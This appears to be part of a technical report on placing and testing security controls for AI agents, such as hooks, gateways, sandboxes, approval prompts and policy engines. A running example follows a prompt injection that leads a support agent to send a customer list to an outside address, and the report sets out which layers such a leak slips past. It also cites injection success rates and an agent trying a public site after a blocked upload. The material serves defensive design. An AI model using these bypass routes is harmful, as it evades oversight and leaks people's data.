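All of these rules need one record that every enforcement point reports to. If the database tool and the email gateway keep separate logs, neither log contains both steps of the leak. The record must also be up to date for each decision, so FORGE delays its verdict until the graph includes everything that led to the proposed action.

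Gaps in the record of earlier actions are hard to avoid. FORGE intercepts tool calls and requests made through common web libraries, but a script that opens a raw network connection bypasses it. In Amazon's product, Dogwood's history automatically follows a request between Amazon's own components, but AWS tells customers who add another gateway to the chain to forward the identifying token themselves. Even Strands Box, an AWS sandbox whose checkpoints share one history, doesn't record reads and writes of files that the user grants directly, according to Help Net Security's *Strands Box*.

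The effect of a gap in the record of an agent's actions depends on how the company writes the rule. Palumbo and colleagues used FORGE to stop a coding agent from publishing code until security scans had covered every recent edit. If the record is missing a scan, FORGE blocks publication and a developer soon asks why, but if it is missing an edit, FORGE lets unscanned code through and nobody notices. Rules that require evidence of an earlier action therefore fail more safely than rules that require its absence. The company can't turn every rule into the safer kind, because some rules require that the agent hasn't done something, such as read the customer list. For such rules, the engine should at least block the action whenever it can't read the record, since an empty log looks the same as one from an agent that did nothing forbidden.

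## What a decision before every action costs

A rule that blocks an action whenever the record is unreadable protects the customer list, but it can also stop the support agent from answering anyone. Other checks can delay the agent, block legitimate actions and take up people's attention. Someone also has to write the policy and keep it up to date.

### Delay

Checks that run as ordinary software take little time compared with the model. Yuan and colleagues, who put a typical model response at 1 to 30 seconds, measured a delay of a few milliseconds for Aegis. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, timed the monitor behind their Cumulative Consent Ledger (CCL), which traces what went into a file before the agent sends it. Other researchers timed their systems in different ways:

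| System | What it checks | Added delay | Conditions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Aegis | Tool calls, through a central server | 8.3 ms median; 1% of calls over 23.1 ms | 1,000 calls in a row, local deployment |
| CCL | Tool calls and the history of their data | 24 ms median | Four virtual processors, complete records |
| AgentBound | An MCP server's access to the machine | 0.6 ms on average | Servers in Docker containers |
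| ZTAC | Requests for files, programs and the network | About 4.0 ms | A request that did no other work |
| ceLLMate | A browser's web requests | About 90 ms per page visit | 11 visits, sitemap with 100 entries |
| Blockaid | Database queries | 2% to 12% of page loading time | Median page, reusing stored decisions |

These tests timed different units of work on different machines, so they don't show which system is fastest.

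A check on system calls has to be faster than a check on tool calls, because one tool call can trigger thousands of system calls. If a script makes 10,000 system calls and each check takes a millisecond, the script runs ten seconds longer. A microVM adds time mainly at start-up, while a network proxy delays every request. A company considering either of these, or a system-call monitor, should measure the delay on its own tasks.

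Checks by a language model are slower. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes two ways to limit the delay. File reads and edits inside the project skip the model check. For other actions, a fast filter gives a one-word verdict, and the model reasons at length only about the actions the filter flags. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* says the check may have a small effect on delay and cost.

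People take even longer to decide. In Hossain and colleagues' study, the median decision took 16 to 39 seconds, depending on how much detail the request showed, and participants were already looking at the screen. Aegis pauses the agent completely for up to five minutes while it waits for a reviewer.

### Legitimate actions refused

As with the command checker CARE, a check that blocks fewer legitimate actions usually misses more harmful ones. When Anthropic ran auto mode on 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, the fast filter alone blocked 8.5% of the harmless calls, and adding the second stage reduced this to 0.4%. But adding the second stage also raised the miss rate from 6.6% to 17% on 52 real actions that went beyond what the user wanted. That sample is small, but the miss rate also rose on 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out, from 1.8% to 5.7%.

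The rate of wrong refusals also depends on the work. BestHub's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports that auto mode stopped 19.8% of harmless actions in a benchmark by researchers at HKUST and ETH Zurich. The benchmark deliberately included vague instructions, so this figure doesn't apply to ordinary work, but a company whose employees give vague instructions should expect a rate above 0.4%.

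Hossain and colleagues measured how blocking actions affects task completion. They used CCL's monitor as a gate on the actions of two agents built on small open models. In 120 attacked runs per agent, harmful effects fell from 52 to 6 for one agent and from 58 to 7 for the other. In 120 harmless runs per agent, completions fell from 104 to 100 for the first and from 110 to 106 for the second, which is a good tradeoff. The tradeoff became much worse when part of the record was missing and the gate blocked everything it couldn't verify, because completion of harmless runs then fell to 76.7%.

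Even a low rate of wrong stops per action can affect many tasks. If a check wrongly stops 2% of harmless actions, and its mistakes are independent, the chance of at least one wrong stop in a task of 50 actions is 1 − 0.98⁵⁰, or 64%. At a rate of 0.4%, the chance is 18%. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that about 10% of sessions at one customer, Gusto, include a refusal. Anthropic presents this as evidence that the check is useful, but the figure doesn't measure how many refusals were correct.

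### When harm is rare

Suppose an agent takes 1,000 actions a day, 1 in 1,000 is harmful, and the check wrongly stops 2% of the harmless ones. If p is the share of actions that are harmful and f is the rate of false stops, the number of false stops for each harmful action is

f(1 − p)/p = 0.02 × 0.999/0.001 ≈ 20.

Even if the check catches every harmful action, a person who reviews the actions it stops should approve about 20 out of 21. A reviewer who approves everything unread would be right about 95% of the time, and might never learn about the 5% they got wrong.

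At the median of 33 seconds per request with CCL, a reviewer can read one agent's 21 daily requests in less than 12 minutes. With 50 such agents, the reviewer would get 1,050 requests a day and need nearly ten hours to read them.

If 1 action in 1,000 is harmful, a check that wrongly stops 2% of harmless actions produces about 20 false stops for every harmful action. Lowering the false-stop rate to 0.4% reduces that to about four. If only 1 action in 10,000 is harmful, the 2% check produces about 200 false stops for every harmful action.

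### What a useful request shows

The reviewer also needs enough information to recognise the harmful request. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in current products show a raw command on a single line.

Hossain and colleagues give an example in which an agent asks to send a file to an auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name all look fine, but the agent made the file from invoice rows that the user had said not to send. A request that avoids this problem might look like this for the support agent:

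```
Task:      "Email Alice a summary of the complaints. No customer records."
Action:    send_email to alice@company.example, attaching report.csv
Effect:    The agent made report.csv from the customer list (steps 2 and 4).
           Alice would receive that file.
Undo:      Not possible after sending
No reply:  The email stays unsent
Options:   Send once / refuse / edit
```

The first three lines of the request follow Hossain and colleagues' design. They repeat the user's instruction word for word, give the action as the monitor recorded it, not as the agent described it, and state the combined effect with links to the steps that produced it. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) recommends the other three.

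Hossain and colleagues tested four kinds of approval request on 80 volunteers, who each made 12 decisions. Participants approved 55.0% of unsafe requests when they saw only a short description, and 43.3% when they also saw the exact arguments. Adding the user's instruction and a full log reduced this to 32.5%. CCL, which organises the same facts around the effect, reduced it to 24.2%. Most of the improvement therefore came from showing the evidence, and the further reduction with CCL could be due to chance. Participants also refused more legitimate requests as they saw more, from 8% with the short description to 14% with CCL.

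An approval request can't show an effect that the system doesn't know about. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) describes a build command that looks routine but runs a malicious package, which reads the user's login key. A person who sees only the command has no reason to refuse it.

### Why people approve requests unread

Half the requests in Hossain and colleagues' study were unsafe, which gave participants a reason to stay alert. In ordinary work, nearly every request is harmless, and people get used to approving them, an effect known as approval fatigue.

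Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's August 2026 post, and an earlier post gave 93%. Anthropic thinks many users are clicking by reflex. They may be, but a high approval rate doesn't prove it, because even a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9% of actions if 1 in 1,000 were harmful.

Anthropic's experiment is better evidence. A research firm hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Anthropic published these results to support making auto mode the default, and the testers had less to lose than developers working on their own code. People who click quickly also reach 50 prompts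 sooner, which could explain the decline. Even so, a 13.6% refusal rate is very low for clearly dangerous commands.

Frequent prompts also encourage people to turn them off. Anthropic found that 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule to allow some shell commands. Many of these rules allowed an interpreter such as Python, which can run anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks bypassed.

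For *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), Salerno, Gao and colleagues interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed another 115. They warn that repeated approval may reflect fatigue rather than a lasting preference, so software shouldn't turn it into a permanent rule. NVIDIA likewise says that a single approval isn't adequate for repeated actions that would break the sandbox's limits.

Fewer prompts don't necessarily lead to better decisions. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people without software backgrounds supervised a simulated assistant that took 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond the user's requests. Some participants approved or refused each action individually. Others first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories of action, such as spending money. The rules cut the average number of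 prompts from 18.0 to 10.9, but the total time, including writing the rules, wasn't reliably shorter.

The group with rules also blocked fewer of the unrequested actions, by about 20 percentage points. They chose "ask" for 81% of their rules, then approved 67% of the unrequested actions they were asked about, compared with 40% in the group that decided every action. The 67% is partly a selection effect, because people who chose "never" didn't see those requests. Selection can't explain the weaker blocking overall, because that figure includes actions blocked by "never" rules. Yan's sessions took only about 11 minutes, so they don't show how either group would behave after weeks of prompts.

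Sandboxing also reduces permission prompts, because the agent can act within fixed limits without asking. Anthropic found that it cut these prompts by 84% in internal use, though a sandbox with no limits could remove even more. Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* claims that Claude works nine times longer between interruptions. Both figures show that people are interrupted less, but neither measures how many harmful actions the system stopped or whether people read the remaining prompts more carefully.

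People may pay more attention to larger decisions. Claude Code users reject 39% of plans and 3% of individual permission requests. But they may reject a plan because they want a different design rather than because the plan is dangerous.

### What a refusal should tell the agent

As FORGE's airline tests suggested, an agent can often recover from a refusal if it knows the reason. Suppose the support agent tries to email the summary to another colleague. It could receive either of these messages:

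```
Error: request failed.
```

```
Refused by policy: this task may email only alice@company.example.
Retrying or using another tool won't change this.
You can save the text as a draft for the employee to send.
```

The first message could describe a network fault, so the agent can reasonably try again or look for another route. But the other route can be worse. For example, when an upload to an internal drive failed at Anthropic, Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site, and auto mode blocked the attempt.

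When auto mode refuses an action, it returns the reason and instructs the model to find a safer way without working around the block. According to Anthropic, a wrong refusal then leads to one retry, and the agent usually finds another way. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, auto mode escalates to a person. If no person is available, the process ends.

The message should distinguish a refusal from a timeout, because only a check that timed out is worth retrying. It should also specify how much the refusal covers. Salerno and colleagues recommend letting users reject either a single action or the whole approach. If the employee refuses an email to a consultant, the message should specify whether the agent may write to someone else.

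An explanation helps an agent that is trying to comply, but it won't stop one that is following a planted instruction, so the rule still has to cover every way the agent could take the forbidden action. Zhong and colleagues studied 290 public reports of agents misusing files, and 77 involved shell commands that could get around restrictions on the agent's built-in tools.

### Keeping the policy up to date

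Zhong and colleagues also compared the default command filters in six coding agents. Codex had 120 rules in about 4,700 lines of code, and VS Code Copilot had 122 rules in about 5,600. The vendors maintain these rules, but each company has to write its own for its data and tools. That can take weeks, as it did with Blockaid. Anthropic calls sandboxing safe but "high-maintenance", because someone must configure each new capability.

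Grouping tools into categories reduces the number of rules, because one rule can cover many tools. Yan built a system in which a language model sorts tools by consequence, such as "delete" or "spend". In a simulation that forbade each category in turn, the system missed 14% of the tools it should have stopped and stopped 4% of the others. Sending uncertain cases to a person reduced the misses to 11% but raised unnecessary prompts to 7%. When Yan ran the model repeatedly on ten difficult tools, the action labels for five of them changed between runs. A person should therefore check the labels for any tool that can do serious damage.

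*A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) sorts actions into categories by how reversible they are and how much damage they could do. It warns that coarse categories block safe actions, while very fine ones become a burden to maintain.

The other problems get worse when nobody maintains the policy. If the company adds a tool without updating the rules, the check blocks legitimate calls. Employees may then approve requests by habit or add a rule that allows too much.

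### Checking beforehand or undoing afterwards

A check is worth its cost if the harm it prevents outweighs the cost of running it and the cost of its mistakes:

p × d × L > k + (1 − p) × f × w.

Here d is the share of harmful actions that the check stops, L is the average loss from one of them, k is the cost of running the check once, and w is the cost of a wrong stop. If the check for the agent with 1,000 actions a day stops 80% of harmful actions and costs almost nothing to run, it is worthwhile when L is more than about 25 times w. If a wrong stop only makes the agent retry once, the loss from most harmful actions easily exceeds that threshold. If a wrong stop takes ten minutes of an employee's time, the average loss has to exceed the value of about four hours of that employee's time.

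L is much smaller if someone can reverse the effect. Several methods use this, or postpone the effect until a person has seen it:

| Method | Example for the support agent | Where it falls short |
|---|---|---|
| Draft | The agent writes an email and the employee sends it | The employee may send it unread |
| Dry run | A command lists the files it would delete | The files may change before the real run |
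| Delayed sending | The mail service holds each email for ten minutes | Nobody may look in time |
| Snapshot | The system saves the folder before each command | It doesn't cover effects outside the folder |
| Undo | The employee cancels a replacement order | The parcel may already be on its way |

Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, a filesystem that holds an agent's changes until the user accepts them. It also takes snapshots, so the agent can inspect what a command did and reverse it. On 11 tasks with hidden side effects, agents found and undid the damage in 8. In the other 3, the changes seemed to fit the task, but the user could still reject them. On 112 routine tasks, agents succeeded 99% of the time, the same as without YoloFS, and needed less input from the user. For ordinary file changes, this looks like a better use of a person's attention than a prompt before every write.

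Zhong and colleagues collected reports of what happens without such a system. Where the outcome was known, 40% of the cases were unrecoverable, 29% took substantial effort to repair, and 31% were easy to fix. People are probably more likely to report serious losses, so the true share of unrecoverable cases may be lower.

Staging and snapshots would have prevented many of the file losses but, like backups, they can't reverse a leak. Secret leaks made up 17% of the harmful operations in these reports, and Zhong and colleagues write that "a leaked credential cannot be unread". The owner can at least cancel a leaked password, but the company has no similar remedy for a leaked customer list. This is why YoloFS still asks for permission before an agent reads sensitive files, although it lets changes wait for review. If the company keeps snapshots, the support agent can safely edit its summary without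 asking, but the check on an email containing customer data has to finish before the email leaves.

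## Comparing and combining the enforcement points

The check on an outgoing email could run in the harness, at a gateway or at the mail service, and different facts about the email are available in each place. Surapani and colleagues compare six placements. In this report's terms, their comparison looks like this:

| Placement | Information available | What it can block | How a harmful action gets past |
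|---|---|---|---|
| Guard next to the model | Tool name and arguments | A proposed tool call | The agent reaches the tool by another path |
| Guard in the harness | The task, its steps and its sub-agents | A step, a tool call or a handover to a sub-agent | The action runs in a different framework |
| Wrapper around a tool | That tool's arguments | A call to that tool | The tool has side effects that its arguments don't show |
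| Gateway or tool server | Endpoint, object, method and token | A request to a service | The request is valid, but untrusted text prompted it |
| Sandbox or operating system | Files, processes and connections | Access to any of these | The agent misuses access that it needs for its work |
| The service itself | The operation, its object and the login | The operation | The login is valid, but the task doesn't call for the operation |

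Surapani and colleagues count network limits as part of the sandbox. Treating them separately makes sense for the support agent, because a proxy that decrypts traffic can read the contents of a web request, which the operating system can't do.

### Task information and coverage

According to Surapani and colleagues, checks near the model have more information about the task, while checks near the resource are harder to bypass. They base this on a literature review and a worked example, and didn't test it by running one rule at all six enforcement points.

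Some experiments support this. Under the same policy, Jing's command gate stopped harmful effects that an operating-system profile allowed. Commey's ZTAC, which rechecks each object when it is used, let far fewer attacks succeed than a tool allowlist did.

But the claim holds only for information about the task. The harness has the employee's request, while the mail service has the current members of a mailing list and the database has the current contents of each row. Moving a check closer to the resource therefore gives it access to some facts but not others. The move also makes the check harder to bypass only for that resource, so permissions on the customer table don't protect last week's export of it.

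A company can weaken the trade-off by sending facts about the task to the resource, for example in a token that works only for September's northern complaints, or by closing every route that bypasses an earlier check. In *Agent Safety is a Box*, AWS engineer Brooker describes the second approach for agents hosted in the cloud. The agent's runtime would block all network traffic except to a gateway, so the agent could not bypass the gateway, which could read the arguments of each tool call.

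Closing the other routes doesn't improve the rule itself. Brooker's sample rule permits refunds below 500, but it checks each call separately, so as printed it would permit ten refunds of 499. Brooker also gives the example of allowing only one refund per order, for which the gateway needs a record of earlier refunds. AWS's Dogwood can now keep such a record within a session.

AWS's Trusted Remote Execution (Rex) closes the other routes for scripts. According to Help Net Security's *AWS open sources Trusted Remote Execution to control what AI agents touch* (2026), agents write these scripts in Rhai, a small language with no built-in access to the operating system. Every file, network or process operation must go through Rex's library, which checks it against a policy just before the system call. Where possible, the library uses a file it has already opened instead of looking up the name again,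 which gives some of ZTAC's protection against a link that changes.

Rex can therefore check the actual operation without predicting what the script will do. But the agent has to write in Rhai and can use only the operations the library offers. Rex also has no information about the task beyond what its policy contains, so a rule that lets the agent read the complaints folder applies even when the task doesn't require it.

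### One email at every layer

Suppose the employee, Maria, asks the support agent to email Alice the summary. The planted instruction makes the agent use the same email tool to send the customer list to records@outside.example. If each layer were the only check, it would give these verdicts:

| Layer | Summary to Alice | Customer list to the outside address | Missing fact |
|---|---|---|---|
| Database | Allows the query for complaints | Refuses the query for customers under Maria's login, allows it under a shared account | Where the data will go |
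| Command checker | Allows the script that reads the complaints | Refuses a script that openly names the old export, can't tell if the script works out the name as it runs | Values that the script computes |
| Sandbox | Allows the script to open the complaints | Allows the script to open the old export if it is in the folder | What Maria asked for |
| Hook on the tool call | Allows, because Alice is on the task's list | Refuses, because the address isn't on the list | Where the text came from |
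| Rules about earlier actions | Allow, unless the agent has also read customer data | Refuse, because the text may contain customer data | Which data the model actually used |
| Gateway | Allows | Refuses if the harness has passed on the task's list, otherwise has to treat all outside email alike | The task |
| Network boundary | Allows the connection to the mail service | Allows the same connection | The recipient and the content |
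| Mail service | Allows, because the token is valid | Allows, because the token is the same | What Maria approved |

Small changes to the attack defeat the hook, even though it looks like the best place for this rule. If the agent sends the customer list to Alice, the hook allows the email, and only the database or the rules about earlier actions would prevent it. If a script uploads the list to a website, the hook on the email tool never runs and the mail service receives nothing. The network boundary, which was useless against the planted email, can stop the upload because the site isn't on its allowlist.

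Surapani and colleagues describe a similar case, in which a meeting invitation tells a calendar assistant to send salary data to an outside address. The enforcement point refuses the agent's attempt to read the salary data and its attempt to send the email. It can do this without anyone recognising the invitation as malicious, because the user asked only for a summary of the week's meetings.

They conclude that only a guard in the harness has the information needed for this decision, and that only a check at the service can guarantee refusal when a call bypasses the harness. The second conclusion is too strong if the network leaves no other route, as in Brooker's design, but it is right for most laptops, where a script can often contact a service directly.

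### When the layers agree

Each control in the trace can work correctly while the whole set still permits a leak. Zhou and Zhang's condition, which the `mail.send` token failed, therefore has to hold for the whole set. The condition is α(E(M(P))) ⊆ ⟦P⟧, which means the policy must permit every effect that the controls allow.

To apply this to the support agent, it helps to list the routes out of the company. On a single route, an effect has to pass every control, so the route allows only what all its controls allow. Across routes, one open route is enough. If Allow(c) is the set of effects that control c lets through, in the policy's terms, then for single actions

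α(E(M(P))) = ⋃ᵣ ⋂ Allow(c), over every control c on route r.

Adding a control to a route can only shrink this set, and adding a route can only enlarge it. A control can't enforce a limit that depends on a fact it lacks, so a mail service that has no record of which recipient Maria approved allows mail to any recipient.

Suppose the policy permits two effects, sending the approved summary to Alice and fetching delivery delays from courier.example:

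| Route | What each control allows | What the route allows | What the policy forbids |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email tool | Hook: any text to Alice. Mail service: any text to anyone | Any text to Alice | The customer list to Alice |
| Script | Sandbox: any file in the folder. Proxy: any request to courier.example | Any file in the folder to the courier | The complaints, or an old export, to the courier |

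Both routes fail the condition, although neither lets the agent write to records@outside.example. The company can fix the first route by having a gateway compare the email with the text that Maria approved. For the second route, the proxy could allow only GET requests to the `/delays` page that carry a month from a fixed list and no other data. Removing the old export from the folder would also help, but it wouldn't protect the complaints.

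The condition rules out only controls that allow too much. Controls that blocked all email would satisfy it but be useless, so the company also has to check that the summary gets through.

A program can check the condition in some cases. Zhou and Zhang require the policy and the tool descriptions to be in a language, such as Datalog, that is simple enough for a program to settle every such comparison. The translation from calls to effects must include every effect a call could have, even if it also includes some that never happen. The agent must also have no unchecked route, so a proof about the email rule depends on the sandbox too. For rules about order or totals, the comparison has to cover whole histories.

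Zhou and Zhang suggest giving each tool an effect contract, a description of what the tool reads, what it sends and to whom, and what it changes. If the contract omits an effect, the check will miss it, so the company has to update the contract whenever the tool changes.

AWS Greenlight, a service in preview, automates part of this work. According to Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (2026), a language model drafts policies from material that the company selects, such as procedures and logs of tool calls. Greenlight then uses automated reasoning to flag conflicting rules and find paths to resources outside the agent's approved access. It installs the approved policy at AgentCore's gateway or in Strands Box, both of which are outside the harness. Using one source for both enforcement points should reduce translation errors, but a person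 still has to decide whether the drafted policy is right.

### Strands Box

Strands Box, which AWS released in October 2026, tries to give one policy the facts from several layers. It runs the agent in a sandbox built on macOS's Seatbelt and provides four checkpoints:

- a shell interpreter for commands;
- a Python interpreter for code;
- a broker for calls to MCP servers;
- a gateway for network traffic.

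The sandbox makes these the only exits. Each checkpoint queries a local Dogwood engine, which blocks any action that no rule permits. All four write to one history, so a rule can connect actions from different checkpoints. In an example from Help Net Security, a rule blocks outgoing web requests after the agent has read a file from a customer-data folder. If the support agent read the customer list with a Python script and then tried to upload it with a shell command, the gateway would block the upload.

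This weakens the trade-off on both sides. The interpreters receive commands and code before they take effect, and the sandbox prevents the agent from bypassing them. The gateway also adds API keys to outgoing requests, so the agent holds only placeholders. When the gateway refuses a request, its response can include the rule that applied. In AWS's demonstration, an agent may post to Slack three times in ten minutes, and a fourth attempt returns an error that identifies the limit.

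The main drawback is the amount of code that a company has to trust. Brooker, who wrote AWS's post on the design, acknowledges that interpreters and protocol interceptors are complex and that "bugs could mean bypassed policy". AWS wrote the code in Rust, a language that prevents many memory errors, and tested it with random inputs. Even so, two interpreters are much larger and more complex than the small mechanism Anderson had in mind, and Li's difficulties with ShellPlan show how many defects even a restricted shell can contain.

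The second drawback is that when a user configures direct access to a file for the agent, the operating system enforces that grant without consulting the policy engine. Reads and writes of the file aren't recorded in the history either. If someone grants access to the customer-data folder this way, the rule against later web requests never takes effect. The company should not grant direct access to such folders, so that the agent has to reach them through an interpreter.

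The rules can be hard to read and write. Brooker says leading coding agents already write them well, but someone at the company still has to understand a rule before approving it. Strands Box is also a developer preview for Macs with Apple silicon, so a company can't yet use it for agents on Linux servers.

### What Anthropic changed

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, an account from 2026, describes a simpler approach. Anthropic limits what the agent can reach and spends less effort on judging each action. It chose a different boundary for each of three products:

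| Product | Where code runs | What it can reach | Why |
|---|---|---|---|
| claude.ai | A temporary gVisor container on Anthropic's servers | Files from that session | The product doesn't need the user's computer |
| Claude Code | A Seatbelt or bubblewrap sandbox on the user's computer | The project, plus whatever else the settings allow | Developers need their own tools and can usually judge a command |
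| Claude Cowork | A virtual machine on the user's computer | Folders that the user selects | Office workers can't be expected to judge shell commands |

Anthropic puts these limits ahead of training and classifiers because training and classifiers sometimes fail. On one benchmark, a single prompt injection succeeded against Claude Opus 4.7 about 0.1% of the time, but the rate rose to 5–6% when attackers could adapt and try 100 times. In an internal exercise where the harmful instruction came through the user, Claude followed it in 24 of 25 attempts. This result is a strong argument for enforcing limits on file access and network traffic outside the model.

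Several of the limits needed revision. Claude Code processed some project settings before the user had agreed to trust the project, so Anthropic changed it to wait for that agreement. Cowork's allowlist checked where data went but not whose account received it, so Anthropic added a proxy that accepts only requests with the virtual machine's own session token.

That proxy sits inside the virtual machine. Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's, so the check has to run where the request's origin is still known. This supports Surapani and colleagues' claim about lost information, but it also has the drawback they would predict, because code inside the virtual machine is closer to the proxy than it would be to a check on Anthropic's servers. If the agent gained full control of the machine's operating system, only two of the machine's six main isolation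 mechanisms would keep working.

Anthropic made another change to improve reliability. At first, the whole agent ran inside Cowork's virtual machine, and no outside process could grant an exception. But if the machine failed to start, the product stopped working. Anthropic moved the agent's loop out and left code execution inside, and says this had minimal effect on security. That is plausible for generated code, which has the same limits as before. But Anthropic also moved local MCP servers out, so a faulty server now runs with access to the user's computer. Administrators therefore have to review these servers like any other installed software.

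Isolation also hid Cowork's activity from companies' own security software, which can't see inside the virtual machine. Administrators can export Cowork's logs afterwards, but they can't monitor it live.

Anthropic concludes that established components held up and its own additions failed. This is a vendor's account of its own products, but it reports failures that Anthropic had reasons to keep quiet. This conclusion also counts against Strands Box, which contains a lot of new code. But an ordinary sandbox can't apply a rule such as "no uploads after reading customer data". A company that needs such rules should put the new checks inside an established sandbox and keep anything the agent never needs out of that sandbox.

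### Where to put checks in three deployments

A coding agent on a laptop does much of its work through shell commands and test runs, so the sandbox matters most. It should cover the file tools, hooks and local MCP servers as well as the shell. The agent should be able to write only to the project, excluding its configuration files, and shouldn't be able to read the developer's keys. A proxy outside the sandbox should block unlisted sites and hold the credentials for publishing code.

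Snapshots let developers undo ordinary edits, so the harness can then ask only about the few actions that affect other people, such as publishing a package. Anthropic found that experienced users approve actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but also interrupt the agent more often. This suggests that developers can supervise an agent without approving every step, provided the sandbox limits the damage it can do before they notice a problem.

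A hosted business agent, such as the support agent, uses a few known services. The company can therefore remove the shell, put every tool behind a gateway and have the network block everything else. Rules at the gateway can restrict recipients and amounts because each tool's arguments have a fixed meaning. The gateway should also hold the credentials so the agent can't use them elsewhere.

The database should apply its own limits. Observer's *Amazon Security Chief Stephen Schmidt on What Customers Really Want From A.I* (2026) reports AWS chief executive Matt Garman's view that an agent working for an employee should inherit at most that employee's permissions, and that many jobs call for fewer. If the support agent can read only September's complaints from the north, a mistake in the recipient rule can expose those complaints but not the customer list. If the agent later has to reply to customers,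 the company can add rules about earlier actions or start a separate agent for each complaint.

Buying a platform doesn't provide all of this. Surapani and colleagues used published documentation to assess MCP with OAuth, Amazon Bedrock Agents and an illustrative arrangement between two organisations. None of the three limited what an agent could learn by combining permitted calls. In Bedrock, one agent could call another without narrowing its authority to the task. Surapani and colleagues recommend adding an independent check on arguments and earlier actions. Dogwood now makes this easier on AWS.

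Madelein van der Hout, an analyst at Forrester, told Observer that the industry hasn't fully solved how to govern agents on several platforms together. A company with such a mix should put more of its effort into checks at its own databases and services, because an agent from any platform has to pass those checks to reach the data.

An unattended agent that runs untrusted code, such as one that tests strangers' submissions overnight, needs the strongest isolation. The code may attack the kernel, and nobody is available to answer a permission prompt. Each job should run in a new microVM with no credentials and no network access, and the system should refuse any request outside those limits. If the tests need packages, staff can install reviewed copies beforehand.

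Cloudflare's *Sandbox* describes a similar setup. The sandbox has its own virtual machine, can't read the agent's storage or credentials, and reaches the internet only if the developer allows it. The sample code turns internet access off and stops each command after 60 seconds. By default, though, all turns of an agent share one sandbox, so the company should give each job a differently named agent so that one stranger's code can't read another's files.

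The harness should stay outside the microVM and treat its output as untrusted. A test report with fixed fields is safer than free text, because a submission could print instructions for the model. Command filters add little here, since the company already assumes that the code is hostile. A microVM isn't the only reasonable choice, since Anthropic uses gVisor for claude.ai, but the extra start-up time is usually acceptable for an overnight job.

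### Testing that each control is active

A configuration file shows what someone intended, so the company should also attempt an action that each control ought to stop. The tests should use dummy records and addresses that the company owns:

| Control | Test | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| Hook or wrapper | Propose a forbidden call to every tool, including new ones | A refusal that names the rule |
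| Command checker | Submit a script that would change a protected dummy file | The file stays the same |
| Sandbox | Read a dummy key and write to the home folder from a script, a program it starts and the file tool | Every attempt fails |
| Gateway | Contact the mail service directly from the agent's environment | No connection |
| Network proxy | Request an unlisted site, then send a forbidden request to a listed one | Neither request arrives |
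| Database | Query the customer table with the agent's login | Permission denied |
| Rules about earlier actions | Read a dummy customer record, then email a test address, first in the same session and then in a new one | A refusal both times |
| Decision point | Stop it, then make a call that the policy permits | A refusal |

Dogwood would fail the second half of the test for earlier actions, so a company that uses it needs another control for data the agent saves between sessions.

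Each test has to reach the control it is meant to check. If the hook refuses an email to the test address, the gateway never receives it, so the gateway goes untested. Testers should therefore send the request directly to each layer, or switch off the earlier checks in a separate test environment. They should also pair every forbidden action with a similar permitted one. A request to a forbidden site may fail only because the site is down, and controls that blocked everything would pass every test in the table.

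Zhou and Zhang argue that an evaluation should cover the unauthorised effects that remain possible as well as what the agent did. If the model ignores the planted instruction in a hundred trials, the company still has no evidence that its proxy works, so a fixed script should attempt the unauthorised actions instead.

The vendor's built-in exceptions also need testing. GitLab's sandbox always permits four destinations, including the customer's own GitLab site, so testing only unknown sites would miss them. GitLab suggests running a test flow that prints evidence of what the sandbox allowed. Van der Hout says customers need their own ways to test controls when one provider supplies the infrastructure, the agent's runtime and the security.

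The quick tests can run before every task, from the same environment as the agent's code, and the task can start only if they pass. The slower ones should run after each update to the harness, the sandbox or the policy. Help Net Security reports that Greenlight shows which recorded calls a proposed policy rule would block, so a team can check whether a rule would stop Alice's summary before they install the rule.
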